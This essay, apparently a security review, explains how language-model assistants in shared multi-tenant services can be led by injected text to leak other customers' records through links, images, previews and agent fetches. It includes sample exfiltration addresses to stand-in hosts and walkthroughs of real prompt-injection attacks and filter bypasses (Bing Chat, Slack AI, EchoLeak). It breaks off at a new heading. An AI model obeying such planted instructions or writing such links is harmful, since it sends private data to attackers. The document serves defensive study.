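# Data leaks between customers through links written by a language model

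## How a summary of several customers' records can leak through a link

A leaking link is a web link or image address, written by a language model, that contains data from the material the model was working on. When somebody opens the link, or a program loads the image, the data goes to whoever runs the server. This can happen to one person chatting with an assistant about their own email. But in a service where one model reads the records of many customer organisations, the data may belong to a customer who had no part in the conversation and no way of knowing that it took place.

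A multi-tenant service is shared by several customer organisations, called tenants. They use the same software, and their records are often stored in the same database tables, with one column marking which tenant owns each row. Booking systems, payroll software and help desks commonly work this way. The arrangement depends on a guarantee, stated as a requirement in *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026), that a request made for one tenant cannot read another tenant's data. Usually, the request names a tenant, and the service checks that the caller may read that tenant's data and filters out other tenants' rows.

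A user's or program's entitlement is the set of tenants whose data it may read. For most accounts that is a single tenant, but some jobs need many. A support desk answers tickets from every customer, and engineers tracing a fault search logs that cover all the tenants. A managed service provider, which runs other companies' computer systems, has administrator access to dozens of clients at once, as does a marketing or accounting agency with many clients. Many firms also have internal tools that query the whole database, because only trusted staff used them. In the hotel-management system that Baig and colleagues studied, most accounts had a small scope, but "portfolio operators", who look after many properties, had a much larger one.

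These people also have the most to gain from a model that can summarize many records in half a page. If a firm gives the model the same access as the person using it, that one model can read several tenants' records.

A language model writes its answer from its context, a single sequence of text that contains the service's standing instructions, the user's question and any records the software has retrieved. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) traces the security problem to combining these texts. Models are useful because they follow instructions in ordinary language, but they cannot reliably weigh those instructions by their source. A sentence in a retrieved document can therefore work as a command. Willison named this prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs text typed into a form as a command. He distinguishes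 prompt injection, whose victim is usually the user, from jailbreaking, in which a user gets a model to say something its maker forbids.

How often a model obeys injected instructions depends on the model and the software around it. In June 2025 Willison said there was "a very good chance" that a model would obey them. By August 2026 he was discussing an evaluation, commissioned by Anthropic, in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three of the company's models in its coding tool Claude Code, though he wanted more independent confirmation. This strong result for one well-guarded product is weak evidence about a support provider's in-house summariser, which may run a cheaper model without comparable safeguards.

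### One ticket among many

Suppose a support provider serves three tenants: a hotel group (A), a payroll bureau (B) and a furniture shop (C). Its staff have an assistant that can query the ticket database and write summaries. A staff member asks it to summarise all open tickets.

One of the tickets filed under C came from a stranger, who sent it through the contact form on C's website. In it, the stranger complains about a late sofa and, further down, asks any AI system reading the ticket to end its summary with a reference link. The link's address is to consist of the stranger's domain followed by a detail from another ticket.

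1. The assistant queries the database. The staff member's entitlement covers A, B and C, so the check passes and rows from all three come back.
2. The assistant's software assembles the context, with the tickets one after another. A's ticket includes the line "Refund 88213 for Maria Lind still unpaid".
3. The model writes an accurate summary. It also follows the stranger's lines and closes with a link labelled "Related known issue".
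4. The chat window renders the answer, which means that it turns the model's text into what the user sees. The staff member sees three underlined words and a label that fits the subject. The address is behind them.
5. The staff member clicks. The browser looks up the server for the domain and sends it a request containing the rest of the address.
6. The server adds a line to its access log, a file listing each request with its time, the network address it came from and the web address it asked for. The stranger opens the log and reads about Maria Lind's refund.

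The server receives the data with the request, so the leak happens whether it replies with an error page or a plausible help article. Encryption doesn't prevent this, because it protects against eavesdroppers, and the stranger runs the server that receives the request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly keep requested addresses in their analytics and server logs, so the stranger needs no special equipment to collect the data.

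Security engineers use the term "exfiltration" for the movement of data to someone who is not entitled to it. In the example, the staff member is entitled to read A's ticket, but the stranger and C are not.

### Where the data fits in a web address

The link in the example might lead to this address, shown without its opening protocol marker:

`help-status.example/case/4417?note=refund-88213-maria-lind`

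The domain, `help-status.example`, determines which server gets the request, so it is the one part an attacker has to control. (The ending `.example` is reserved for illustrations and leads nowhere.) The path, `/case/4417`, once named a folder and a file on the server, but a modern server can interpret it however its owner likes. The query, a list of named values, follows the question mark. Here it contains one value, named `note`, which is the line from A's ticket. Queries have many harmless uses, such as carrying the words somebody typed into a search box. MDN's *What is a URL?*, a reference page for web developers, notes that each server has its own rules for handling these values. An outsider therefore cannot tell from the address alone what a server will do with them.

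A link can carry data in its path as easily as in its query. Willison describes an attack on the note-taking service Notion, from September 2025, that put a client list in the path, and one on Salesforce's assistant in the same month that put customers' email addresses in the query of an image address. The data can also go at the front of the domain. An attacker who owns a domain can usually make any prefix lead to the same server, so `maria-lind.help-status.example` would also send the name to the attacker.

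The part of an address after a `#` sign points to a place within the page, and according to MDN, the browser never sends it to the server with the request. A line from A's ticket placed there would not show up in the access log. After a click, though, a script on the page that opens could still read the line and send it on.

Common web servers accept addresses several thousand characters long, which leaves room for a summary of several customers' records. A model can condense what it has read to fit, and it can encode the text so that a person who hovers over the link sees a string of letters and digits, similar to the tracking codes in newsletter links.

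### Four ways the request gets sent

An address in an answer leaks data only when something sends a request to it. In current products, four things send such requests.

Of the four ways a link can leak the records, the user's click is the simplest and the only one that gives a person a chance to stop the leak. The chance is small because the link appears in an answer the user asked for, from a tool their employer provides, under a label that the attacker has in effect chosen. Willison counts both clickable links and direct network calls as ways for data to leave the system.

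Many chat programs let the model write in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images. If the answer contains an image address, the program turns it into an image, which the browser fetches as soon as the answer appears, without a click. The image can be a single transparent pixel. Any request that software makes without a click is called an automatic fetch.

Leaks through links first came to notice this way in the spring of 2023. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a post on a security blog, describes an attack on the chat assistant in Microsoft's search engine and browser, which could read the web page the user had open. An attacker could plant instructions on that page, for instance in a comment or an advertisement, for the assistant to write an image address containing a short encoded summary of the page and the conversation, along with any passwords it found. In the demonstration,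 the image appeared only after a couple of further exchanges, so the user had no reason to connect it with the page. The researcher reported the flaw on 8 April 2023 and heard on 15 June that Microsoft had fixed it. The fix included a content security policy, a rule a website sends to the browser that lists the domains from which it may load images and other content.

The same month, Roman Samoilenko showed a version for ChatGPT. A website secretly added instructions to any text a visitor copied, and the visitor then unknowingly pasted them into ChatGPT. According to *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023), OpenAI began to mitigate the problem only in December 2023. Both attacks stole data belonging to the person using the assistant, so they are evidence that data can leave through a web address, but not that it can cross between customers.

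Data can still leak through images. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, May 2026) reported that the agent in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email the user's own inbox without asking for approval. Those emails could include external images, and opening an email sent a request for its images.

People tend to overlook link previews as a trigger for leaks. When someone posts a link in a chat program such as Slack, Teams or Telegram, the program fetches the page so that it can show a title and a thumbnail. Developers call this unfurling, and Slack does it by default for posted links, according to its *Unfurling links in messages*. Slack also has a help page for website owners who have found its preview robot in their access logs, which is where the stranger in the example would look. The robot fetches as little of the page as it can, but this doesn't prevent the leak, because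 the data is in the request and the page can be empty.

If the provider's staff talk to their assistant in a Slack channel, a link preview can leak the records before anyone reads the summary. Willison (2024) raised this danger in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* and passed on a remedy from the security researcher Johann Rehberger: an application that posts to Slack can switch off previews for its own messages.

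The security company PromptArmor later invited people to test their own combinations of agent and messaging program. Its article *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that a preview makes the same type of network request as a click. The company set up a website that logged every preview request it received and the data each one contained. Participants could claim a log entry and name the combination behind it, or report a combination that had produced no preview. One published entry contained a name and an API key, the kind of password one program uses with another. OpenClaw, a popular open-source personal assistant, was exposed under its default settings when people used it through Telegram, but one line in its configuration file turned the previews off.

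*AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* (Apostol) also lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Microsoft's kit for building agents, and Slack with certain bots among the combinations reported as risky. The article adds that the messaging company's server makes the request. A firm that monitors only its own network would therefore not see the data leave. Volunteers chose what to test, so the results show which combinations can leak but not how common they are. Like the image attacks, these results concern only how data gets out.

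The remaining trigger is an agent fetching the link itself. An agent is a model connected to tools that it can use on its own, often including a web browser or a search function. The address doesn't have to appear in the agent's answer. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built a test system in which a user asks for a summary of a web page, and instructions hidden in the page's title or description lead the agent to send a request containing private data from its context. The user gets an ordinary summary, so checking only the text of the answer would not reveal the leak.

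The data also doesn't have to be inside any single address. In July 2026, *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) described an attack on Anthropic's Claude that has since been blocked. The attacker's site already had a page for each letter of the alphabet, and the agent spelled out the user's name by the order in which it visited those pages.

### Two failures in one leak

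The example combines two failures that can each occur alone, and most of the published evidence is about one or the other.

Data crosses between tenants when a line from A's ticket and an instruction from C's ticket meet in the same context, and the instruction determines what happens to the line. In the example, the assistant was authorised to read all three tenants' tickets because the staff member wanted them all summarised. Suppose instead that the staff member had asked only about the late sofa. The task scope, meaning the tenants that the request concerns, would then be C alone. But the assistant would still be entitled to read A's and B's tickets, and the stranger could include text in C's ticket telling it to look them up. Baig and colleagues point out that the service's check passes in such a case, since the account is entitled to those tenants. They treat the problem as a variant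 of the "confused deputy", a program that an outsider induces to misuse its authority. They list support tickets, inbound email and suppliers' PDFs as places where an outsider can put text that shapes what an agent requests.

The other failure is that output reaches an outsider. This takes no second tenant at all, as the Bing Chat and ChatGPT attacks show.

Data can also cross between customers without a link. If the model includes Maria Lind's refund in a reply that the provider then sends to C, one customer has seen another's data. The distinction matters when judging defences, because restricting which images may load would not stop that reply, and even perfect isolation between tenants would not stop a user's own data from leaking through an image.

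### Willison's three conditions

According to Willison, a system is open to this kind of theft when it has access to private data, takes in untrusted content, and can communicate with the outside. He calls this combination the lethal trifecta. The attacker uses the untrusted content to give the system an instruction to find private data and send it out. Removing any one of the three conditions prevents the theft, although the remaining two may still cause other problems.

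Willison wrote the test for individuals who connect their assistants to a mix of tools. Their private data and untrusted content often come from separate places, such as a folder of documents and a web page, so they can at least choose whether to combine them. The test also fits a shared ticket database, but there the same rows are both private and untrusted. C's tickets should be kept private from A, and A has no reason to trust their text. A query that returns several tenants' tickets therefore meets two of the three conditions by itself. Willison notes something similar about email, where access to an inbox supplies private data and also lets any stranger write to the model.

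A leak needs private data, untrusted text and a way to send the data out, and Willison considers the last of these generally the easiest to remove. Vendors have mostly taken this approach, with rules that restrict which links and images a model's output may use. Removing the private data would defeat the purpose of the tool, and a support desk can hardly remove the untrusted text, because its job is to read what strangers send.

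### Leaks with no attacker

An accidental leak needs only two of the conditions, private data and a way out, and nobody has to plant anything. Suppose the staff member asks for help with a printer fault at tenant B, and the model adds a link that searches the manufacturer's forum for the error message, along with a device name and a contact from A's ticket. Or it links to a supplier's claim form with the fields already filled in, and puts A's telephone number where B's should go. Both kinds of link carry their contents in the query, so when the staff member clicks, the search engine or the supplier receives A's details, though it isn't looking for them.

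A similar leak appears to have happened at scale, through a different fault. heise online's *ChatGPT prompts apparently appeared in Google Search Console* reported in November 2025 that website owners had found what looked like whole ChatGPT prompts, some of them very personal, in a Google tool that shows them the searches that led to their sites. Jason Packer, one of the two consultants who investigated, counted about 200. He thinks a step meant to reduce a prompt to a few search terms passed on the entire prompt, though he is not certain. OpenAI said that it had fixed an error affecting a small number of search queries, but did not confirm the rest of the account. If Packer is right, the prompts went to owners of unrelated websites who had done nothing to get them.

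Searches can reveal a lot even when each one looks harmless. *Agents That Know Too Much* (Lahjouji and Colaco, 2026), a survey of privacy in agents, lists an agent's queries as one of the places where data escapes, separately from its final answer. *MosaicLeaks* (Gurung, Gella and colleagues, 2026) measured this with 1,001 research tasks, most of which required an agent to alternate between a company's private documents and the public web. An observer saw only the agent's web searches, in order. In one example, an agent searches twice for a grocer's online traffic growth in 2020, then searches for something else that involves the figure 15%. From the three searches together, the observer can conclude that the grocer's online traffic grew by 15%.

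With one small model, Qwen3-4B-Instruct, the observer recovered at least part of a private fact in 34.0% of runs. Training the model only to do the research better increased the leakage. Gurung and colleagues designed the tasks to encourage leaks and describe the setting as a stress test, so the rate is not an estimate for everyday use. The result does show that an agent can leak private facts without an injected instruction.

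Agents show the same tendency when they fill in forms. *GapLeak* (Cheong, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested web agents on tasks such as returning a purchase or applying for a job, where the website asked for something the user had not supplied. A person would probably leave the field empty. The agents tended to search other available sources, such as the order history in the user's account, and then submit more than the task required, including details of other people such as travelling companions and job referees. Across three agent frameworks and six models, the average rate of unauthorised disclosure was about 37%. The form's operator is the adversary in the study and words the help text to draw out more information, so these leaks are not quite accidental. But the page contains only visible, ordinary requests like those on many honest forms, and closing the gap between what the form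 requested and what the user had provided cut disclosure by more than half.

All of these cases involve a single user or a single company, so they are relevant to data leaving but not to data crossing between tenants. Applying the form result to the support provider also requires assuming that an agent missing a telephone number for B would treat A's ticket as another source it could use.

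## What formal analysis says about the leak

Testing measures how often an assistant leaks under the conditions tested. Formal analysis uses definitions to derive what a system permits in every case those definitions cover, including cases nobody has tried. For leaks through links, it helps determine which tenants' records an outsider can get an assistant to read and how much of that material a link can transmit.

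### A program that used its authority for the wrong person

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an incident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code, and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in its own directory, so the operating system let it write to any file there, including the billing records. One user learned the name of the billing file and entered it as the file for the debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

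The user wasn't allowed to access the billing file, but the compiler was. The compiler had two sets of permissions, its own and those of whoever ran it, and a request to open a file didn't specify which set applied. Hardy calls such a program a confused deputy. Tymshare added a way to switch between the two sets, but some applications soon needed more than two. Hardy instead proposes using capabilities, which are references that both identify a resource and authorise its use. Under that scheme, the user would have had to give the compiler a capability for the billing file, which the user didn't have.

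In the support provider's case, the stranger who writes through C's contact form is in that user's position. The stranger can't read A's tickets, but the assistant can. Lan and colleagues point out that with the compiler it was unclear whose authority applied, whereas with an agent it is unclear what the person in charge intended.

In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk gave the first formal characterisation of freedom from such attacks in terms of a programming language. They relate it to integrity, which concerns what untrusted input may influence. A leaking link also breaches confidentiality.

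### The stochastic deputy

Baig and colleagues adapt Hardy's idea to language models with tools, which they call stochastic deputies. A stochastic deputy has authority over more resources than a request needs, and it selects which to use. Its selection is not guaranteed to be correct, and the same input can produce different selections. Instructions and data reach the deputy through a single channel, so anyone who can place text there competes with the user to direct the deputy.

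Telling the model to stay within one tenant is a weak remedy because that instruction is just more text in the shared channel. Testing can't certify the model either, because the selection is unreliable. Clean tests limit how high the failure rate could plausibly be, but they don't show that it is zero. Willison discussed 720 failed injection attempts against Claude Code. Even if those attempts were independent and typical of future attacks, a true success rate of about 0.4% would be compatible with the result at the 95% confidence level. At that rate, 10,000 poisoned tickets would produce about 40 successful injections.

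Baig and colleagues therefore assume that the attacker completely controls the model's behaviour, so any result they can still establish holds for both weak and strong models.

### A correct check that lets the wrong data through

Let E(*p*) be the entitlement of a user or program *p*, meaning the set of tenants whose rows *p* may read. When a request from *p* names a tenant *t*, the service returns *t*'s rows if *t* belongs to E(*p*) and refuses otherwise.

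This works well for ordinary software, where the program's code determines *t*. To change it, an outsider would have to alter the code or steal a password. When a language model makes the request, *t* is part of the model's output, and a sentence in a ticket can change it. One successful injection can then reach

Reachable(*p*) = the union of Rows(*t*) over all tenants *t* in E(*p*)

which is every row of every tenant that *p* may read.

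Suppose A has 40 open tickets, B has 25 and C has 15. An employee of the furniture shop who logs in to see the shop's own tickets has the entitlement {C}, so the reachable set is 15 tickets. The provider's staff member has the entitlement {A, B, C}, so the reachable set is 80 tickets, even when the staff member asks only about the late sofa. The service then handles the model's possible requests as follows, where D is a customer that this staff member doesn't serve.

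| Tenant the model names | Is it in the entitlement {A, B, C}? | Is it in the task scope {C}? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| C | yes | yes | rows returned |
| A | yes | no | rows returned |
| D | no | no | refused |

The second row describes the breach. The check works as its designers specified, but it doesn't take the task scope as an input. In the 373-trial experiment by Baig and colleagues, a check of this kind served every such request that a model made. They also note that logging these requests doesn't help much afterwards, because in their system a query for the wrong tenant within the entitlement looks the same as a correct one.

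### Scope confinement and its limit

Baig and colleagues designed their system to achieve scope confinement. This means that every row returned in *p*'s session must lie within Reachable(*p*), whatever sequence of tool calls the model makes, even if an attacker chose the sequence. The system takes the tenant's name out of the request and derives the permitted set from a signed login token instead.

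They argue that this achieves the goal, but say the argument isn't a machine-checked proof. It assumes that all data leaves the database through the code that applies the filter, that the login system lists the right tenants for each user, that nothing alters the permitted set while a database connection is open, and that no connection passes from one user to the next with the old set still attached. The last assumption is easy to break by accident, because services often share connections to run faster.

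If the assumptions hold, the furniture shop's employee can't obtain A's tickets, whatever the model does. This guarantee is strong for the many accounts that cover one tenant, but much weaker for the provider's staff member, who is allowed to read all 80 tickets, including the one with the line about Maria Lind's refund. The assistant could read A's ticket on the stranger's instruction and put the line in a link without violating scope confinement. Scope confinement therefore doesn't protect A from C, or from a stranger writing through C's form, when one person is allowed to read both tenants' tickets. Baig and colleagues acknowledge that their goal confines reads to the credential's entitlement, which may be wider than the one tenant intended for the session.

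The provider could narrow the entitlement by opening a session for C alone whenever the task concerns C, which would reduce the reachable set to 15 tickets. This is close to Hardy's remedy, since the assistant would receive authority only over what the task designates. But it wouldn't help with a request to summarise all open tickets, because all three tenants are then in scope. Scope confinement also limits only what the assistant reads, so an assistant that satisfies it can still write that data into a link's address.

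### Noninterference

A definition that covers both the crossing between tenants and the exit through a link is much older. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, describe a system as a machine with a set of users. Each command a user gives may change the machine's state, and an output function determines what each user sees in each state. One group of users does not interfere with another if deleting all the first group's commands would never change what the second group sees. In symbols, for every sequence of commands *w* and every user *u* in the second group,

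output to *u* after *w* = output to *u* after *w* with the first group's commands removed.

A's records enter the ticket system through A's actions, so the requirement for tenants is that changing A's data must not change what C can observe. Goguen and Meseguer call a group isolated when no information flows into or out of it, which is what customers of a shared service generally expect.

Applying the definition to a summary with links means comparing two versions of the same morning, identical except that A's ticket reads "Refund 88213 for Maria Lind still unpaid" in one and "Refund 40672 for Jonas Falk still unpaid" in the other. In each version, the assistant summarises all the tickets, the staff member clicks the link, and the stranger's server logs the request. If the two log entries differ, A's data has interfered with what the stranger sees, whether the name appears in the query, in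 the path or as a string of code. The definition also covers a model that adds an ordinary link only when A has an unpaid refund, because then one log has an entry and the other has none, even though a filter that searches addresses for names and numbers would find nothing.

The stranger is neither a tenant nor a user of the ticket system, so the analyst has to add them to the model as an observer. Goguen and Meseguer assume that the output function contains all the information the system gives to users, and they don't describe what people learn in other ways. An analyst who counted only the words in the chat window as output could prove a summariser secure while its image requests were sending A's data to the stranger. The analyst has to count every image request, link preview and fetch by the agent as output too.

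The original definition also assumes a deterministic machine. A language model given the same tickets twice may write two different links by chance, so a difference between two runs doesn't prove that data has leaked. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) therefore use a probabilistic version in *The LLMbda Calculus*, which compares how likely each observation is under the two versions of the secret data. They give computer-checked proofs that it holds for every program in their small language for building agents. Like most guarantees of this kind, theirs allows some leakage through whether a program finishes.

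### Allowing useful disclosure

Strict noninterference would rule out many useful summaries. Suppose A's ticket mentions a failed card payment and the model adds a link to the card company's public status page. If the staff member clicks it, the card company's log depends on A's ticket. This leak is tiny and probably harmless, but strict noninterference still forbids it.

Dongol (2026) makes the same objection in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, using the example of a calendar assistant that answers meeting requests from anyone. The assistant discloses its owner's availability by design, so it violates noninterference. The traditional fix is a policy that lists what each task may release, but somebody has to write one for every task. Dongol instead compares the agent with an imaginary reference agent that follows the same plan under the same controls but never obeys untrusted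 text. The real agent is relatively secure if an attacker can't use it to distinguish any two secret values that the reference agent would have kept indistinguishable.

One of the worked examples closely resembles a leaking link. An agent looks up its owner's account number, reads an email and displays a summary. It can also fetch web pages, although the task doesn't require it. The agent follows an instruction in the email to fetch an address ending in the account number, and the attacker reads the number from the request. The reference agent never fetches anything, so the leak is due entirely to the injection.

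Dongol proposes a fence, in which the software around the agent permanently withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted text. A computer-checked theorem shows that this makes every plan relatively secure against an attacker who sees the contents and order of the agent's outgoing requests. If the fence comes after the agent reads the email, an injected request can go out before the agent loses its tools.

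The theorem requires a trusted planner to fix the steps before the agent reads anything untrusted. It treats each injection as a single tool call and requires that secrets not affect when the model obeys. All tool calls must pass through the control software, and the attacker must not see the ones it refuses. Dongol also assumes that showing the user a reply has no effect the attacker can see, and gives loading an image as an example of what this rules out. The assumption is false for a chat window that loads images from addresses the model has written. The control software would stop the support assistant from fetching the stranger's address itself, but it wouldn't stop the staff member's browser from fetching it to load an image or after a click.

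The comparison with a reference agent also offers little protection against accidental leaks. If ordinary summarising puts A's telephone number into a supplier's form, the reference agent does the same, so the disclosure counts as part of the task. Dongol also points out that the definition depends on which secrets an attacker can distinguish and does not limit how much one request reveals. Suppose a task lets an outsider guess a secret code and answers only "right" or "wrong". An injection that sends the outsider the entire code still counts as relatively secure, because for any two possible codes there is some guess that would have told them apart.

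### How much a link can carry

The amount of information a link can leak is easy to calculate. Information theory measures it in bits. One bit settles one yes-or-no question, and *n* bits can distinguish 2ⁿ possibilities. *Model Counting Modulo Theories* (2015) proves that a program can leak at most the logarithm of its number of possible outputs. It leaks that maximum when the secret fully determines the output and all outputs are equally likely. *Quantifying information flow in interactive systems* (2019) has a matching theorem for deterministic systems in which the observer also supplies input, as the stranger does by writing a ticket. In that case, the outputs to count are those the observer could see given their input.

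The upper- and lower-case letters, the ten digits, the hyphen and the underscore make 64 symbols that are safe to use in the path or query of an address. If the model can choose freely among them, each character can carry 6 bits, because 2⁶ is 64. An address with 2,000 free characters can therefore carry 12,000 bits, or 1,500 bytes. That is enough for about 250 words of plain English without compression, or for 600 six-digit codes.

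If the assistant may request only addresses from a fixed list, it can't write data into them, but it can still leak data through its choice of address. A choice among *N* addresses carries log₂(*N*) bits, provided that the attacker can tell the requests apart. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* describes an attack in which 36 existing pages stand for the 26 letters and ten digits, and the agent visits them in the order that spells out the data. Each visit carries about 5.2 bits.

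A six-digit code, such as those used to reset passwords, has a million possible values, so identifying it takes 19.9 bits. Three visits, each to one of 36 pages, have only 46,656 possible sequences, which is too few to distinguish every code. The number of visits needed depends on what reaches the attacker's log.

| Conditions | Visits needed | Possible messages | Bits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Order visible, repeats allowed | 4 | 1,679,616 | 20.7 |
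| Order visible, no repeats | 4 | 1,413,720 | 20.4 |
| Order lost, no repeats | 6 | 1,947,792 | 20.9 |

The conditions correspond to practical obstacles. As Embrace The Red explains, browsers cache loaded pages, so a repeated visit may never reach the server, and requests can arrive out of order. The post suggests preventing an agent from opening the same address twice in a session. That makes very little difference to the leak of a single short code, but it limits how much a whole session can leak. With 36 pages, the attacker gets at most about 140 bits if the order of visits is visible, and 36 bits if it isn't. The limit grows with the number of pages, so a thousand pages can carry 1,000 bits in one session even when the order is lost, because each page is either visited or not.

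These figures are upper limits, and real agents make mistakes. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) had agents choose among four references on a page, then used the resulting requests to infer which reference matched each agent's private task. When each reference had its own address, the inference was correct in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal. When the order of the requests carried the information, accuracy fell to 67.9%. If each of the four visits in the password example were 93.8% reliable and the errors were independent, the complete code would arrive correctly about 77% of the time. This estimate is rough because the agents in the study were choosing sources relevant to their work, not spelling out a code. An attacker could also add a visit or two to check the others for errors.

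In other respects the figures in the table are too low, because they count only which pages the agent visited and in what order, while a server's log also records the time of each request. Liang and colleagues list timing and the number of requests as further channels, though timing was the least reliable of the six they tested, with 58.6% accuracy.

An attacker can also combine small leaks. Garby and colleagues illustrate this with CaMeL, a system that tracks where data goes in an agent's program and blocks forbidden uses. Whether CaMeL blocks a run can depend on a secret, and the outcome then reveals one bit. The retry loop around the tracking isn't tracked, so an attacker who can keep triggering retries can extract the whole secret one bit at a time. Twenty suitable yes-or-no answers are enough for a six-digit code.

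### What a list of exact addresses can guarantee

A list of trusted domains hardly limits how much data a link can leak, because it doesn't restrict the path or query. The 12,000 bits then go to whoever runs the trusted domain. OpenAI warns that many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other addresses, so a request that starts at a trusted domain can end at an attacker's server.

OpenAI's rule therefore applies to complete addresses. ChatGPT may fetch an address automatically if an independent crawler, with no access to users' conversations, has already recorded that exact address on the public web. Since the address existed before the model chose it, the model can't have written Maria Lind's refund into it. OpenAI claims only that the rule is meant to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself.

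Limiting links to pages in a crawler's index makes stealing bulk data, such as a summary of several customers' records, slow and easy to notice. Spelling out 12,000 bits with 36 pages takes about 2,300 visits, compared with one visit if the model can write any address. The attack on Claude that spelled out a user's name showed that short secrets remain exposed. If an attacker could get a million pages of their own into the index, one for each six-digit code, a single visit would reveal the code. The attacker benefits only from pages whose requests they can observe, so the total size of the index matters less than it may seem.

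The rule also has to cover every route by which a request can leave. If an address isn't in the index, OpenAI may warn the user and let them open it anyway. If the user accepts, the link can again carry the full 12,000 bits of a free address, and the protection depends on the user's judgement.

A list does not achieve noninterference if it leaves the assistant any choice. Even a list with one entry can carry one bit, because the assistant can either request the page or not. The capacity is zero only when the number, timing and addresses of the requests are the same whatever A's records contain. An assistant could meet that condition by fetching a fixed set of pages every morning before it reads any tickets, but not by looking up the page needed for a particular ticket.

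## Attacks shown on deployed assistants: from one organisation to an outsider

Since 2024, security researchers have repeatedly used outside text to make commercial assistants put private data into a link or an image address. The seven attacks described below targeted products from Slack, Microsoft, Salesforce and Atlassian, and the makers have since blocked them all. These attacks are evidence about the second half of the leak, in which data leaves. In each case the data came from the organisation or person whose assistant was attacked, so none shows one customer's records reaching another.

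### Slack AI: a secret released by a click

Slack AI lets people ask questions about their company's Slack messages in ordinary language. It searches the private channels the user belongs to and every public channel in the workspace, including those the user has never joined. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, from August 2024, describes how one member of a workspace could exploit this combined search to steal information from another member's private messages.

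In the demonstration, a developer had saved an API key in a private channel with no other members. The attacker created a public channel, also with no other members, and posted one message in it with instructions for the model. If anybody asked for the key, the model was to add it to a web address the attacker owned and present the result as a link for signing in again. When the developer later asked Slack AI for the key, the search put both messages into the same context. The answer looked like a loading error followed by an invitation to sign in. Clicking the link sent the key to the attacker's server.

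The attacker had no access to the private channel and didn't need to know what was in it. The victim would also have had trouble tracing the theft, because Slack AI cited only the developer's own message as its source, and the attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results. But in a second demonstration, where a user asked about a manager's messages and received a phishing link with no stolen data in it, Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel.

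PromptArmor reported the flaw on 14 August. Five days later Slack replied that it found the evidence insufficient, because the information in the first video came from a public channel, which every member can search. The attacker's message was in a public channel, but the theft depended on combining it with a private message. PromptArmor then published its findings, and Slack announced a patch the next day, according to SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing*. Slack said at the time that it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data.

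SC Media describes the attacker as an insider. This is accurate for the version PromptArmor demonstrated, since posting requires an account in the workspace, but an outsider may have been able to attack through files. On the day of the first report, Slack AI began to read uploaded files and connected Google Drive documents as well as messages. An employee who downloaded a PDF with hidden instructions and uploaded it to Slack would then have unknowingly brought in the attacker's text. PromptArmor considered this attack highly likely to work but had finished its tests before the change.

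### EchoLeak: one email past four defences

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions using a person's work email, chats and files. Researchers at Aim Labs found that a single email from a stranger could make it send out whatever internal data was in its context. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* reports that the researchers told Microsoft in January 2025, that Microsoft completed the fix in May, and that Aim published the details on 11 June. Aim named the flaw EchoLeak, and its public vulnerability identifier is CVE-2025-32711.

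The recipient didn't have to open the email. It stayed in the inbox until the recipient asked Copilot a question to which the email seemed relevant, and Copilot retrieved it along with internal documents. To make retrieval more likely, Aim wrote a long email with sections on subjects employees often ask about, such as onboarding and leave.

Microsoft had prepared for emails of this kind. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, an academic case study, describe the attack as a chain of bypasses, each of which defeated a separate defence:

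1. An injection classifier, a program that labels incoming text as safe or suspicious, checked the email. Aim worded the instructions as if they were addressed to the human recipient and never mentioned Copilot or AI, and the classifier let them through.
2. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers. But Markdown also has a second way to write a link, which puts the label in the sentence and the address further down, like a footnote. The filter missed that form.
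3. The same notation works for images, which the chat window loaded automatically.
4. A content security policy allowed images only from approved domains. One of them hosted a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch an outside address on request. The attackers pointed the image at that service and put their own address inside the request.

The last step works because one web address can contain another. If the support provider's chat window trusted a preview service, the stranger who complained about the sofa could have the model write an image address like this one:

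`previews.trusted.example/fetch?page=help-status.example/refund-88213-maria-lind`

The browser checks only the domain at the front of the address against its list, finds it there and sends the request. The trusted server then requests the second address, and Maria Lind's refund appears in the stranger's log.

EchoLeak shows that multiplying the failure rates of several defences underestimates the risk from an attacker who can experiment. If each of four defences stopped 90% of attacks and their failures were independent, only one attack in 10,000 would pass all four. But an attacker who can experiment looks for an input that each defence misses, then combines these inputs in one email. Three of Microsoft's four defences recognised a particular form (suspicious wording, the usual way of writing a link, an approved domain), and the same content could take another form.

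Aim described EchoLeak as the first zero-click vulnerability in an AI product. "Zero-click" means that the victim doesn't have to click a link or open a message, although the victim did have to use Copilot. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, called it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. The Bing Chat attack of 2023 had also used an image that loaded without a click, though the user needed to have the attacker's page open. EchoLeak matters mainly because it succeeded against a product with defences built for this threat.

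According to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, Aim rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10. Microsoft said that nobody had exploited the flaw and that customers did not need to do anything because the company had fixed it on its own servers.

### ForcedLeak: a sales form and an expired domain

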